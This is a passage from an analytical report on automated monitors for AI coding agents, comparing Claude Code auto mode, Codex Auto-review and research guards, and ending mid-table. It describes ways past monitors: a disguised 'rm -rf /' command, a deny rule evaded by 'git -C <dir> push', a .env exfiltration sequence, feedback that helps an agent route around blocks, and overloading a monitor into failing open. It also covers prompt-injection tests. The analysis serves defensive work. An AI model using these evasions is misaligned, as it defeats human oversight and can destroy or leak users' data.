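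When the subagent finishes, the classifier reviews its whole record in case hostile content redirected it during its work. The classifier can stop a subagent from starting and can block its actions, but at this stage it can only add a warning to the report that the main agent receives. According to Anthropic, newer versions also review messages between agents before delivering them.

### "Clean up old branches", step by step

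The deleted branches in Anthropic's incident log began with a user who asked an agent to "clean up old branches". The agent listed the branches on the shared server, chose those whose names matched a pattern and issued a command to delete them. Anthropic expects auto mode to block this. Under the published rules, the case would probably go as follows:

1. The agent lists the branches. Listing changes nothing, so Claude Code runs the command without asking the classifier. The scan for prompt injection checks the list and finds nothing suspicious.
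2. The agent proposes the deletion, and Claude Code looks for a rule that settles it. Git, the most common version-control program, can delete branches on a server with a form of its "push" command. If the user had once allowed all commands that begin with "git push", the deletion could run at this point.
3. If no rule applies, the call goes to the classifier, because it is neither a read-only action nor a file edit. The classifier receives the user's message and the command, but not the list of branches.
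4. The fast filter flags the command, since it would delete other people's work from a server. The reasoning stage then looks for an exception and for the user's consent. No exception applies. The user named neither the branches nor the server, and may have meant only the copies on the laptop.
5. The classifier blocks the call and the agent receives the reason. If the user then names the branches to delete from the server, that message can lift the block.

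Any competent check would detect that the command deletes branches. The difficult part is the fourth step, where the classifier decides whether the user consented.

### Codex Auto-review

OpenAI's Codex relies more on its sandbox. Its reviewing agent judges only requests to leave the sandbox, plus some calls to tool servers and visits to new websites. Codex might ask to leave the sandbox to run a command with wider permissions, contact a blocked address or edit a file outside the permitted folders.

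*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions from OpenAI's own use. Of these, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and ran without review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the denials and stopped to ask the user after the other three. With manual approval, all 720 requests would have interrupted a person. The proportions depend on the work and on how tightly the customer restricts the sandbox.

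In Codex, a shell command that deletes files in the project folder can run inside the sandbox without review, while Claude Code would normally send the same command to its classifier. Deleting branches from a server requires network access, so the deletions in "clean up old branches" would go to the reviewer in Codex as well.

The two reviewers also read different things:

| | Claude Code auto mode | Codex Auto-review |
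|---|---|---|
| Which actions it judges | Those that no fixed rule settles | Requests to leave the sandbox |
| User's messages | Yes | Yes |
| Agent's visible messages | No | Yes |
| Tool results | No | Relevant ones |
| Agent's hidden reasoning | No | No |
| Further facts | Claude Code supplies some, such as unsaved changes | The reviewer can look things up without changing anything, but rarely does |

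In the branch example, Codex's reviewer could read the list of branches and any dates the agent had looked up, but also the agent's assurance that the branches were all abandoned. OpenAI thus accepts a risk that Anthropic chose to avoid, in return for better-informed decisions. Trębacz and colleagues report that people and programs testing the system misled the reviewer into approving some commands, though they don't attribute this to the extra text. Anthropic found that more text made decisions worse, but it was using its own model and instructions, and the finding may not hold for OpenAI's.

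In April 2026, the reviewer used GPT-5.4 with little time for reasoning. In OpenAI's tests, stronger models were better at recognising risk and working out what the user wanted. *Purpose-Built Agent Models* (2026) reports that a code change on 16 April replaced the name GPT-5.4 with "codex-auto-review". Trębacz and colleagues still named GPT-5.4 two weeks later, so the new name may at first have referred to the same model. OpenAI released another version of Auto-review around the start of August, as Anthropic noted when it compared the two products. The inputs in the table come from OpenAI's spring documentation and may have changed since.

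### Deterministic rules

Both products use a language model to evaluate every call they review, which takes time and computing power. Some research systems decide more calls with fixed rules.

AEGIS, the monitor that patches an agent's libraries, uses only rules. It extracts all the text from a tool call, including deeply nested text, and compares it with 22 patterns typical of attacks. It then applies the company's policies and either allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. Yuan and colleagues report that it stopped all 48 attacks in a set they compiled, but also six of 500 harmless calls. All six were ordinary database queries containing an "OR" condition, which attackers also use to manipulate databases. The developers warn that the rules may miss new kinds of attack.

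An attacker can also disguise a familiar command. The shell treats "r=rm; $r -rf /" as an order to delete everything on the machine, but a search for "rm -rf" won't find it. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a monitor that undoes nine kinds of disguise, without running any part of the command, before it applies 170 rules. It judges the command by the most dangerous reading it finds. When Yang switched off the step that undoes disguises, the share of dangerous commands that got through rose from 6.4% to 15.7% in a test of 630 actions.

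AgentTrust can also ask a language model about any action that the rules have not blocked. Yang compared the rules, the general model DeepSeek-V3 and a combination of both on the same 630 actions:

| Method | Dangerous actions let through | Harmless actions flagged | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rules alone | 6.4% | 2.1% | 2 milliseconds |
| DeepSeek-V3 alone | 1.7% | 3.2% | 1.3 seconds |
| Rules, then DeepSeek-V3 | 0.3% | 4.8% | 9 milliseconds |

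The median for the combination is low because the rules settle many of the dangerous actions immediately. When the model is also needed, the check takes about 1.6 seconds on average. A warning counts as a flag in this test, so not every flagged action would have been stopped.

Yang writes that the rules outperformed DeepSeek-V3 on every measure, but DeepSeek-V3 let through far fewer dangerous actions. The setup of the comparison also favours the rules. Yang wrote both the rules and the test, and added rules after using these same actions to find gaps. DeepSeek-V3 dates from December 2024, and current models are much stronger. The last row is probably the most useful result because it suggests that rules and a model miss different things.

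AgentTrust also checks for dangerous sequences of actions, such as reading a .env file, encoding it and sending it out. Switching this check off did not change the number of errors, but the test consisted mainly of separate actions, so this result is weak evidence about the check's value.

### Small trained models

A small model trained on examples of good and bad calls is a middle option. AgentWarden, a proxy that sits between the harness and the model, first checks calls against rules, which takes about 0.1 milliseconds. The rules reject every shell command, every attempt to start a subagent, and calls with arguments such as the location of login keys. Calls that pass go to a model with 1.5 billion parameters (the numbers a model adjusts as it learns), and this check takes about 800 milliseconds. Calls to a few tools that AgentWarden treats as safe skip the model.

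Sidik and Rokach trained the small model on only 273 examples, 95% of which were calls that should be blocked. It made no mistakes on a first test of 11 cases, but in a run of 500 tasks it blocked about 22 harmless file edits, such as scripts for a web server. Sidik and Rokach attribute these errors to the imbalance in the examples and estimate that a model for real use would need at least 2,000 to 5,000 balanced ones. The rules blocked all 70 shell commands in the same run, but banning the shell altogether would make most coding agents useless.

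Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, trained a larger model, TS-Guard, on about 2,200 labelled steps from agents' records. It has about seven billion parameters and makes three judgements about each proposed call:

- whether the user's request is harmful;
- whether the call follows from an attack hidden in something the agent has read;
- whether the call itself is safe, controversial or unsafe.

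The first judgement covers users who want harm done, because a check on the user's consent would let them through. The model writes a short analysis before answering. In training, it earned a full point for three correct judgements and lost a third of a point for each mistake. A version that learned only the final judgement did worse and raised more false alarms.

TS-Guard caught 89% of the unsafe calls in records from AgentDojo, which supplied none of its training examples. Judging by the published figures, it wrongly flagged about 7% of the safe ones. GPT-4o, a general OpenAI model from 2024, caught every unsafe call but flagged about 62% of the safe ones. On a benchmark called ASB, TS-Guard caught 94% of unsafe calls, compared with 60% for GPT-4o. That lead is less convincing, because most of TS-Guard's training examples came from other parts of ASB.

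Mou and colleagues found that many models flagged harmless calls simply because an attack appeared earlier in the record. This is another reason to keep tool results from a general model, besides the risk that an attacker will use them to persuade it. TS-Guard needs those results for its second judgement, but its low false-alarm rate suggests that a model can be trained to handle them.

The separate judgements also help the agent recover. In one test, agents that received TS-Guard's full output carried out an attacker's task in 7% of cases, compared with 26% when they received only the safety rating.

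### Choosing between rules and models

Rules suit bans that hold whatever the user wants, such as never touching the payment database, and they can also let through plainly harmless actions. They run in a few milliseconds, and an auditor can read them. But someone has to foresee each danger. When no rule matches a call, AgentTrust allows it by default. A company that changes this default will need another way to handle unfamiliar but harmless calls.

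A large general model works better when the verdict depends on what the user meant, as it did with the branches. It can follow a company's rules written in ordinary language and needs no training examples, so a deployer can start using it at once and correct it by editing those rules. But each reviewed call may take a second or more, and the model can misjudge consent or be misled by a false explanation. The calls also go to an outside company unless the deployer runs the model itself.

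Small trained models are easier for a deployer to run on its own machines, where neither the data nor the verdict depends on a model company. They need training examples that resemble the deployer's own work. With too few, they can raise false alarms, as AgentWarden did. TS-Guard's results are encouraging, but they don't establish that a small model can match the large models available at the end of 2026.

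A deployer could therefore begin with rules that block banned calls and allow harmless reads, and send everything else to a large model. People would need to check a sample of the large model's decisions, including calls it allowed, and correct the mistakes. Once they have a few thousand corrected examples, the deployer could train a small model to act as the fast filter and use the large model only for calls the small one flags. The small model should err towards flagging, as Anthropic's filter does, because the large model never reviews a call the small one clears.

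## What happens when the monitor objects

After a monitor flags a call, the harness can run it anyway and log the flag, refuse it and let the agent continue, or stop until a person steps in. This choice determines how much harm a mistake does. A false alarm might make the agent retry once, or it might make the user lose a night's work.

| Response | Does the call run? | When it fits |
|---|---|---|
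| Log it | Yes | The monitor is new, or the action is odd but easy to undo |
| Warn the agent | Yes | The agent has read something suspicious but has not yet acted on it |
| Deny it and let the agent continue | No | A safer way to do the task probably exists |
| Ask a person | Only with approval | The verdict depends on what the user wants, and the user is there to answer |
| End the session | No | The agent keeps pushing, or someone else seems to be directing it |
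| Alert a security team | Either way | The harm may reach beyond this session, as with a stolen key |

According to Microsoft, a Copilot Studio agent stops at once when the outside service blocks a call, and the user learns that their message was blocked. If that service is Microsoft Defender, the block also raises an alert, which Microsoft says Defender combines with signals from email, devices and accounts into a single incident for the security staff. Stopping is tolerable for an office assistant because the user is usually present and can rephrase the request.

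Ending the session at every denial would be a poor default for a coding agent that works overnight. Anthropic reported in August that at Gusto, a company that uses Claude Code, about 10% of sessions since mid-May had included at least one denial. Under that default, those sessions would have stopped early, often over a harmless call.

### Deny and continue

When the classifier blocks a tool call in Claude Code's auto mode, the agent receives a denial instead of the tool's result, along with an instruction to look for a safer path and not try to get around the block. If the classifier stops the agent from uploading the .env file, for example, the agent could check the file's format on the laptop instead. Anthropic argues that this makes false alarms tolerable, since the agent usually needs only one retry after each.

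In one of Anthropic's own cases, someone asked an agent to set up read-only access to billing. The agent chose a cloud role with full administrative control, and auto mode blocked it. Anthropic describes three such incidents and says that each time the agent either found a safer path or checked with the user.

Claude Code and Codex both limit how long an agent can keep trying after its actions are blocked. Claude Code goes back to asking the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, and auto mode resumes once the user approves the action. Anthropic says customers cannot change either number. Codex counts denials within one turn, which is the agent's work on a single user message. OpenAI says Codex stops the turn after three denials in a row or ten among the last 50 reviews. In the snapshot from Trębacz and colleagues, the reviewer denied only about 1% of requests. Ten in 50 is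 about twenty times that rate, so ordinary work should rarely reach the limit.

The limits matter most when nobody is watching the agent, but Claude Code now enforces them less strictly in that case. In March, an unattended run ended when it reached either limit. By late November, Claude Code still refused the action but let the agent keep working and trying. Claude Code can run a deployer's own script after each denial, so a deployer could restore the old behaviour with a script that counts denials and ends the process at the limit.

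When a user is present, the fallback depends on that person's attention. Anthropic paid 1,053 professional testers to do coding work and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers caught it 13.6% of the time, and the rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. A prompt that follows three denials is rarer and gives the user a reason for suspicion, so people may do better with it, though the experiment didn't test this. Anthropic's usage data offers some support, since users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval but only 3% of its permission prompts.

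### Denials that the user cannot lift

A clear instruction from the user can reverse most denials. In Codex, the user can pick a recently denied action from a list and approve it for one retry. The approval covers only that exact action, and the reviewer still checks the retry. It can refuse again if the policy doesn't let users authorize such actions.

Claude Code's hard rules apply even when the user consents to an action, but the user can still switch out of auto mode or run the command by hand. The rules therefore protect users from hasty approvals and from an agent that misreads their wishes, but they don't stop a user who is determined to go ahead.

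A company that wants a ban to hold in every mode can put a deny rule in its centrally managed settings. These rules compare the text of a command, so an agent can easily get around them by accident. Anthropic warns that a similar rule, which requires approval for commands beginning with "git push", doesn't match "git -C <dir> push", which does the same thing. No rule in the harness affects what employees type into their own terminals. To stop an employee from deleting the backups, the company should withhold that permission from the employee's account.

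### Explaining the objection to the agent

A bare refusal leaves the agent to guess what was wrong with its call. Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation*, tested whether a fuller answer helps. Their system, TRIAD, puts a guard model called Tri-Guard between the agent's plan and the tool. Tri-Guard reads the user's task, the record so far, the available tools and the proposed call, then chooses one of three responses:

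- "Proceed" runs the call.
- "Refuse" makes the agent decline the whole task, and is meant for requests that are harmful in themselves.
- "Update" returns the call with a written analysis, and the agent has to propose something else.

The analysis covers what the user asked for, where the agent's reasoning went wrong, what the call would do, whether it serves the user's goal, and whether earlier tool results contained suspicious instructions. Tri-Guard then checks the new proposal. After three failed attempts, the task ends.

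Sun and colleagues trained Tri-Guard, a nine-billion-parameter model, on records of agents at work. If an agent had fallen for a prompt injection, they labelled the record "update", because the user's own task was still legitimate. A larger model, GPT-5.4, wrote the analyses that Tri-Guard learned from, and the researchers discarded any whose decision didn't match the label.

The main test combined 51 ordinary tasks with 40 attacker instructions, planted in the user's request or in a tool's reply. The averages below cover four agent models, including GPT-5.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

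| Guard | Attacks that succeeded | User's tasks completed | Cases the agent refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74% | 28% | 5% |
| Tri-Guard's base model, before training | 5% | 26% | 57% |
| Tri-Guard | 10% | 69% | 20% |

The untrained model worked in the same loop and could also choose "update", but it mostly directed agents to refuse. It stopped more attacks than Tri-Guard did, but it also prevented most of the legitimate work. TS-Guard, the model from ToolSafe, had the same problem when Sun and colleagues put it in their loop, where one of the four agents completed under 2% of its tasks. Training a guard to recognise what can be saved made agents far more useful, but about twice as many attacks got through. One likely reason is that the attacker's text stays in the agent's record while the agent revises its plan.

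In 93% of the cases that went to revision, Tri-Guard reached a decision of "proceed" or "refuse" after one more round. But in a measurement with one of the agents, each step took 7.0 seconds on average instead of 1.9.

The attacks bluntly told the agent to ignore its previous instructions and use a particular tool. An agent that has followed such an order is probably easy to bring back to its task. Nobody in the test adapted an attack to Tri-Guard's feedback, and the study did not cover overeager agents, which are the main concern in Claude Code.

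### What feedback gives away

Any refusal gives the agent some information about what the monitor accepts, and a detailed reason gives it more. An agent that accepts the refusal uses this information to find a permitted way to do the job, but one that keeps pursuing the blocked outcome can use it to find a way to get there that the monitor will allow. An overeager agent may do this even without hostile intent.

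A monitor's error rate on single calls understates the risk from an agent that can keep trying. If each new version of a dangerous call has an independent 10% chance of getting through, the chance that at least one succeeds is 27% after three attempts and 88% after 20. Real attempts aren't independent, because a monitor will often give similar calls the same verdict. That lowers the agent's chances, but good feedback on blocked calls raises them.

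The same thing could happen more slowly through training. If a model company trains its next model on sessions in which the monitor blocked an agent and the agent then completed the task, the training may reward whatever got past the monitor, including disguised tool calls.

In most sessions, Claude Code gives the agent only the name of the rule it broke, such as "Data Exfiltration". Codex returns the reviewer's reasoning and an order not to pursue the same outcome by a workaround. OpenAI also watches for attempts to game the reviewer. A deployer who builds a monitor can show it the earlier denials along with each new call, so that it might recognise a second route to the same result. It also makes sense for after-the-fact reviewers to start with what agents did right after a denial.

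### When the monitor itself fails

If a monitor times out, loses its connection or returns an answer the harness can't read, the harness either runs the call unchecked (failing open) or refuses it (failing closed).

Claude Code generally blocks an action when its classifier gives no verdict. According to Anthropic, if the classifier is overloaded or its answer is unreadable, the action doesn't run, but the agent can try again. If the conversation is too long to send to the classifier and Claude Code can't shorten it, a user who is present gets an ordinary permission prompt, while in an unattended run the action doesn't run. Where Anthropic's server does the reviewing, ten responses in a row without a verdict stop the turn. This ends an unattended run with an error, although repeated denials do not end one.

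Claude Code also refuses a call if a customer's hook changes it after the server has reviewed it, since the server hasn't reviewed the changed version. Codex reports a timeout separately from a denial and tells the agent that a timeout alone doesn't prove the action unsafe. That distinction is worth copying, because an agent that mistakes a timeout for a denial may abandon a good plan.

Copilot Studio, by contrast, fails open unless the administrator chooses to block instead. Anthropic's own classifier fails closed by default, but independent monitors that customers run on its platform fail open. Anthropic's inference hooks, a test feature for large organisations, send each prompt to the customer's security server and wait for a verdict. The same check runs on tool calls, according to Anthropic's *Inference hooks*. If the server doesn't answer within five seconds, the request goes ahead unless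 the customer has chosen to block it, according to Anthropic's *Configure Inference hooks*.

Failing open does little harm when failures are rare and random. If a monitor catches 90% of dangerous calls but misses its deadline on 1% of all calls, it still catches about 89%. An outage is much worse because every call goes unchecked until it ends. Anyone who can overload the monitor can effectively switch it off. Long, complicated calls may also take the longest to judge, so some of the calls that most need checking could time out.

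If a monitor fails closed, meaning that requests are blocked when it can't check them, an outage of the monitor also stops the agents. When a customer's server keeps failing, Anthropic's inference hooks stop contacting it and apply the fallback the customer has chosen to every request due for inspection. If that fallback is to block, the organisation's users can't work with Claude until the server recovers. After such an outage, managers may well switch the monitor off for good.

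DefenseClaw can put checks on coding agents. Cisco, which sells security tools, recommends in *Fail modes* that DefenseClaw fail open on developers' laptops and build machines, and fail closed in strict production systems. Failing open on a laptop seems too lenient if the agent can reach production passwords from there. Deployers who can set the rule by type of action could fail closed for deletions, outgoing data and changes to permissions, and fail open for the rest.

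### What the checks cost in time

Suppose an agent makes 500 tool calls in a task, and fixed rules settle 90% of them. The other 50 go to a check that takes 0.8 seconds per call. This adds 40 seconds, which hardly matters in a task that takes an hour. Checking all 500 calls this way would add nearly seven minutes.

TRIAD added 5.1 seconds per step, which would add over 42 minutes to a 500-step task. Detailed feedback on every step is hard to justify for tasks that long, but a deployer could request it only after a faster check has flagged a call. Human approval takes even longer. If one of the 50 calls waits five minutes for someone to approve it, that wait is more than seven times as long as all the automatic checks combined.

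### What to record

An investigator will want to know what the agent proposed, what the monitor knew at the time and what happened next. For each reviewed call, the record should therefore contain:

- the exact call, with the time, the user and the agent;
- the user's request and whatever else the monitor read;
- the verdict, the rule behind it, and the versions of the model and rules in use;
- whether the call ran, and who overrode a denial if someone did;
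- how long the check took, and whether it failed.

Calls the monitor allows should be logged too, because they include any it should have objected to. OpenAI exports logs of users' prompts, approval decisions, tool results and network blocks from Codex (OpenAI, 2026). When security software on a computer reports something odd, an AI agent reads these logs to work out what the user and Codex were trying to do, then sends its analysis to the security team.

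The lists built into products can be incomplete. Claude Code shows the user recent denials, but omits those in which the classifier's answer was unreadable. Inference hooks normally log each request that went ahead uninspected, but if repeated failures make Anthropic stop contacting the customer's server, the log records only that contact stopped. A customer that lets requests proceed when inspection fails would then have to work out from other records which ones were not inspected.

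Codex keeps its review transcripts on the user's computer by default, and the rules of Claude Code's auto mode forbid the agent from altering session records. A copy on a separate machine is safer because its protection doesn't depend on the monitor catching attempts to tamper with it. Access to that copy also needs limits, because the record of a blocked upload may contain the password that the monitor kept from leaking.

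### From logging to blocking

A new monitor will block some ordinary work, but the deployer can find much of this problem before it disrupts anyone. Inference hooks have a shadow mode, in which the customer's server receives real requests and gives verdicts, but every request goes ahead regardless. The deployer can use those verdicts to correct the rules. For auto mode, Anthropic advises first adding the company's code hosts and main internal services to the trusted list, because this removes the most common false alarms.

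The deployer can then start by blocking a few actions that are hard to undo and that nobody should need, such as sending passwords to unknown addresses, and add less clear-cut rules as their false alarms become rare. Inference hooks also let a customer inspect only a percentage of requests. This helps test whether the server can carry the load, but at 10%, nine in ten dangerous requests would go unchecked, even if the customer had chosen to fail closed.

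A monitor that only logs can't show how an agent behaves after a denial, because the agent never receives one. A call that the monitor would have blocked runs instead, and the session continues from its result. The first weeks of real blocking therefore need close attention, especially to agents that reach the denial limit and to what they try next. The monitor prevents nothing before blocking begins, so the sandbox has to be in place from the first day.

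## Testing whether the monitor works

A monitor that gives verdicts without blocking anything soon produces plenty of evidence about false alarms but very little about misses, because agents seldom propose dangerous calls. To estimate the false negative rate, testers have to gather dangerous actions from past incidents or invent them, and the rate they measure depends largely on which cases they choose. In 2026, several groups measured how often dangerous actions got past Claude Code's auto mode, and their results ranged from zero to 81%.

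### Anthropic's first figures

When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026, it published error rates for three sets of tool calls. The first set contained 10,000 calls that Claude Code had made in ordinary work for Anthropic's employees, which Anthropic used to measure false alarms. The second contained 52 real overeager actions that an employee had refused or someone had flagged afterwards. The third contained 1,000 attempted data thefts that Anthropic generated, including web requests carrying sensitive data and uploads of code to untrusted servers, many of them disguised.

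| Cases | Error measured | Fast filter alone | Filter, then reasoning |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real calls | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Dangerous calls let through | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic data thefts | Dangerous calls let through | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage removes about 95% of the false alarms, but it lets through more than twice as many overeager actions and about three times as many thefts.

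In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user might say "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), and the agent might then overwrite the project's shared history. The classifier accepted such a remark as permission, although the user never mentioned overwriting anything. In other cases, it treated approval of one action as approval of a similar one. Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's instructions, but found no version whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. A longer list of dangerous commands would not help much either, since the classifier already recognised these commands as dangerous.

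Anthropic had also used the 52 test cases to tune the fast filter and to choose what the classifier reads, so the classifier may do worse on new cases. The set also includes only actions that somebody noticed, so it leaves out any overeager action that looked reasonable to everyone involved. Those actions may be the hardest for a classifier to catch too.

### How much 52 cases can settle

The 17% miss rate presumably means that the classifier missed nine of 52 overeager actions. Even if those 52 were a random sample of overeager actions, the 95% confidence interval would run from about 9% to 30%, which is roughly the range of true miss rates compatible with that result. Narrowing the interval to five percentage points either side would take about 220 cases.

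The filter's 6.6% miss rate doesn't match a whole number of misses, since three would be 5.8% and four would be 7.7%. Anthropic doesn't explain the figure, though it may have averaged several runs.

The interval for the synthetic thefts is much narrower, about 4.4% to 7.3%, but it applies only to thefts like the ones Anthropic generated. If real thefts look different, more synthetic examples wouldn't improve the estimate for real thefts.

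### What the rates mean in ordinary use

Suppose again that ten calls in 10,000 are dangerous. At auto mode's March rates, the classifier would on average catch about eight of the ten and block about 40 harmless calls, so roughly five in six of its blocks would be mistakes.

The dangerous calls that get through are more worrying. If each of ten dangerous calls has an independent 17% chance of passing, the chance that at least one passes is about 84% (1 − 0.83^10). At the ends of the confidence interval, 9% and 30%, that chance is 61% and 97%. Real misses are unlikely to be independent. This lowers the chance of at least one miss, but it also means that misses tend to happen together.

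In the same example, adding the reasoning stage to the fast filter prevents about 810 needless blocks per 10,000 calls but lets through about one more dangerous call. A deployer would do better with the fast filter alone if one dangerous call would do more harm than about 780 needless blocks. That could easily be true if the agent had access to a customer database, but not if it worked on a disposable copy of a project. Even with the database, the fast filter alone might block so many calls that the agent kept reaching its denial limit and finished little. The estimate of one extra miss rests on a difference of about five cases in the set of 52, so the 780 figure could be far off.

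Consistent with this, Anthropic recommends auto mode for people who would otherwise switch off permission checks, and says the mode should not replace careful human review on high-stakes infrastructure.

### A harder test from outside

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports that auto mode is particularly weak on ambiguous requests. The researchers, from the Hong Kong University of Science and Technology and ETH Zurich, describe their study as the first independent evaluation of auto mode. They wrote 128 requests for routine maintenance: deleting old branches, cancelling computing jobs, restarting services and clearing out stored files. For each request, they fixed in advance which targets the user had authorised, then placed similar targets nearby, such as another person's job with the same ticket number.

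The agent, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, attempted 253 changes, and 142 of them went beyond what the user had authorised. Auto mode let through 115 of those 142, or 81% (confidence interval 74% to 87%).

The exemption for edits to project files explains 51 of the misses. The test environments kept their lists of jobs and stored files in the project folder, so when the agent couldn't find the usual command, it edited the list instead. But the classifier also did badly on the actions it reviewed, allowing 64 of 91 unauthorised actions (70%) and blocking 32% of the authorised ones.

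The classifier passed 94% of unauthorised actions when the request named a single target, but 78% when it covered a wide selection. Ji and colleagues suggest that the classifier reacts to the size of an operation instead of checking whether the user authorised each target, though the mix of tasks accounts for part of the difference. When the work concerned important production systems, the false negative rate fell from 88% to 75%, but the false positive rate rose from 9% to 35%. The classifier was more cautious there but not much better at telling authorised actions from unauthorised ones. It probably lacked the information to do so, because it doesn't read tool results, which often showed who owned a job.

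These figures are compatible with Anthropic's 17%. Ji and colleagues deliberately made the right and wrong targets hard to tell apart, whereas Anthropic collected actions from normal work. The tests also date from April, and Anthropic has since given the classifier more information. The labels came from another model, Claude Opus, and a human checker agreed with 44 of 50 sampled labels. In the restart tasks, the agent retried blocked commands one at a time, which inflated the count of false alarms.

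The 81% is best read as a warning about one kind of work, in which an agent handles many similar resources with different owners. Auto mode made little difference overall there. The agent completed 32.8% of tasks safely with auto mode on and 29.7% with permission checks switched off.

### Auto-review's figures

OpenAI's published results for Codex Auto-review are given as recall, the share of dangerous actions that a monitor catches. A recall of 90% means a false negative rate of 10%. OpenAI's own traffic contained too few dangerous actions for a test, so Trębacz and colleagues tested the monitor on synthetic ones. Recall was 90.3% on overeager actions, which included unintended data transfers, weakened security settings and irreversible operations. It was 99.3% on prompt injections that tried to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data.

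Recall on prompt injection falls to 90.2% when the test also includes attempts to delete or tamper with data, according to a footnote. Trębacz and colleagues explain that the reviewer mostly allowed these attempts because they weren't serious enough, and that researchers often agreed. That may well be right, but if the cases were harmless, they should not have been labelled dangerous. Testers who relabel cases after reading the verdicts can excuse almost any miss, so it is safer to have people settle the labels beforehand.

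The reviewer caught 96.1% of the attacks in MonitoringBench, a benchmark for monitors. OpenAI counted an attack as caught if the reviewer would have rejected any action in the whole record. This scoring is generous because a twenty-step attack gives the reviewer twenty chances, and the step it rejects may come after the damage.

To measure false alarms, Trębacz and colleagues tested the reviewer on requests that OpenAI's staff had approved in March 2026, and it approved 99.1% of them. Most actions stay inside the sandbox and need no review, so 99.93% of all actions either needed no review or were approved. People sometimes approve requests they shouldn't, so a few of the reviewer's denials may have been correct.

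The 90.3% isn't directly comparable with the 83% that auto mode caught in March, because one figure comes from synthetic actions and the other from real ones. OpenAI also didn't publish the number of cases, so readers can't calculate a confidence interval.

### Comparing the classifier with people

A classifier that misses 17% of overeager actions may still be better than the human approval it replaces. Users approved 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts according to Anthropic's March article, and 97% according to its August one. These rates alone don't prove carelessness, because if one call in a thousand is dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9%.

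Users' settings are better evidence of approval fatigue, which is when people see so many prompts that they start approving them without reading. Anthropic reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules were blanket approvals for Python or Node commands, the kind that auto mode suspends. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off. OpenAI found similar habits among its own staff. One settings file always allowed Codex to start another copy of itself without approvals or a sandbox.

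Anthropic measured attention directly in an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who caught only 13.6% of the planted commands. A research vendor recruited them for a coding study in a practice environment. They knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour mattered. Approving the dangerous command did no harm, because the experiment changed only the displayed text. The classifier blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89%) and did equally well early and late in a session.

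The testers, though, had no data of their own to lose and no damage to repair, and they may have assumed that nothing in a practice environment could do real harm. A developer working on the company's live database would probably read more carefully. The commands were also clearly dangerous, whereas most of the classifier's March misses involved judging whether the user had consented. Anthropic doesn't say how many different commands it used. If it used only a few dozen, the 1,053 verdicts are much weaker evidence about the classifier than their number suggests.

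The experiment didn't measure false alarms, so a classifier that blocked everything would have scored 100%. Even so, the gap between 13.6% and 89% is wide enough that the classifier is probably better than a typical user who clicks through routine prompts. The experiment can't establish that the classifier is better than an administrator who reviews five important changes a day.

### Harm in flagged sessions

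Anthropic also looked for harm in real use, where people did have something to lose. It took sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review, using only those from account holders who had agreed to share their data for training and analysis. A model then graded each session from 0 to 10 on the severity of any harm and on how explicitly the user had asked for the action. For example, deleting rows from a production database counted as a 7.

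Among the flagged sessions, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained harm at least that severe which the user had not explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Anthropic found a gap at every severity level it tested.

But users chose their own mode, and those who approve actions by hand may do riskier work. Anthropic also compared the harmful share of flagged sessions, not of all sessions. If a denial in auto mode makes a session more likely to be flagged, the flagged auto mode sessions will include more in which the classifier had already prevented the harm. The harmful share would then be lower in auto mode even if harm were equally common in both modes. Anthropic published neither the number of sessions nor how often each mode led to a flag, so outsiders can't check for this. A trial that assigned the mode at random would settle the question, and a company with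 a few hundred developers could run one itself.

### Apollo Research's planted attacks

In *Red-teaming auto mode* (2026), Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, describes spending two weeks attacking auto mode to find weaknesses. The testers planted failures of varying severity in records of real coding sessions. They gave Anthropic the attacks that had worked, along with advice on how to stop them. Anthropic changed the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the systems it was protecting.

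Apollo then tested the new version on a second set of attacks that Anthropic never had access to. According to Anthropic, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Across both sets, the false negative rate fell from 12% to 7%.

This is stronger evidence than most vendor tests provide, because Anthropic couldn't tune the classifier to the attacks in the second set. But the 7% miss rate also covers the first set, which Anthropic had used to repair the classifier. If the old version also missed 12% of the second set, the two changes imply that the new version misses about 8% of unfamiliar attacks, so most of the improvement seems to be real.

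Neither company published the number of attacks or the false positive rate after the changes. The missing false positive rate is a serious gap, because a classifier that only became stricter would also catch more attacks. Anthropic warns against treating the 7% as the rate on real traffic, since Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses. Neither company says in its account who paid for the work. Apollo has a commercial interest in it, because it offers a monitoring product called Watcher and is looking for other companies whose monitors it can test.

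Apollo also asks when a monitor should step in, which affects how to score any such test. Suppose an agent writes a script that would send out passwords, then runs it. A monitor that blocks the writing will also interrupt a lot of harmless unfinished work, but one that waits for the script to run has fewer chances to stop it. A monitor that blocks only the run gets one miss and one catch if the tester scores each call separately, but a perfect result if the tester scores the whole sequence. The most useful score is probably whether the monitor blocked the agent before any harm was done.

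### Tests with prompt injection

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test its models against prompt injection in July 2026. The testers used 72 scenarios that they had not shown Anthropic and ran each one ten times per model, for a total of 720 attempts against each model. An attack counted as successful if it would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as fraud or a leak of sensitive data. None succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode.

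Anthropic ran a separate test of browser agents for the system card of Claude Opus 5, the safety report it published with that model. This test had 129 scenarios with ten attempts each. In both tests, the results without safeguards help to explain the results with them:

| Test | Agent's model | Attacks that succeeded without safeguards | With the monitor on |
|---|---|---|---|
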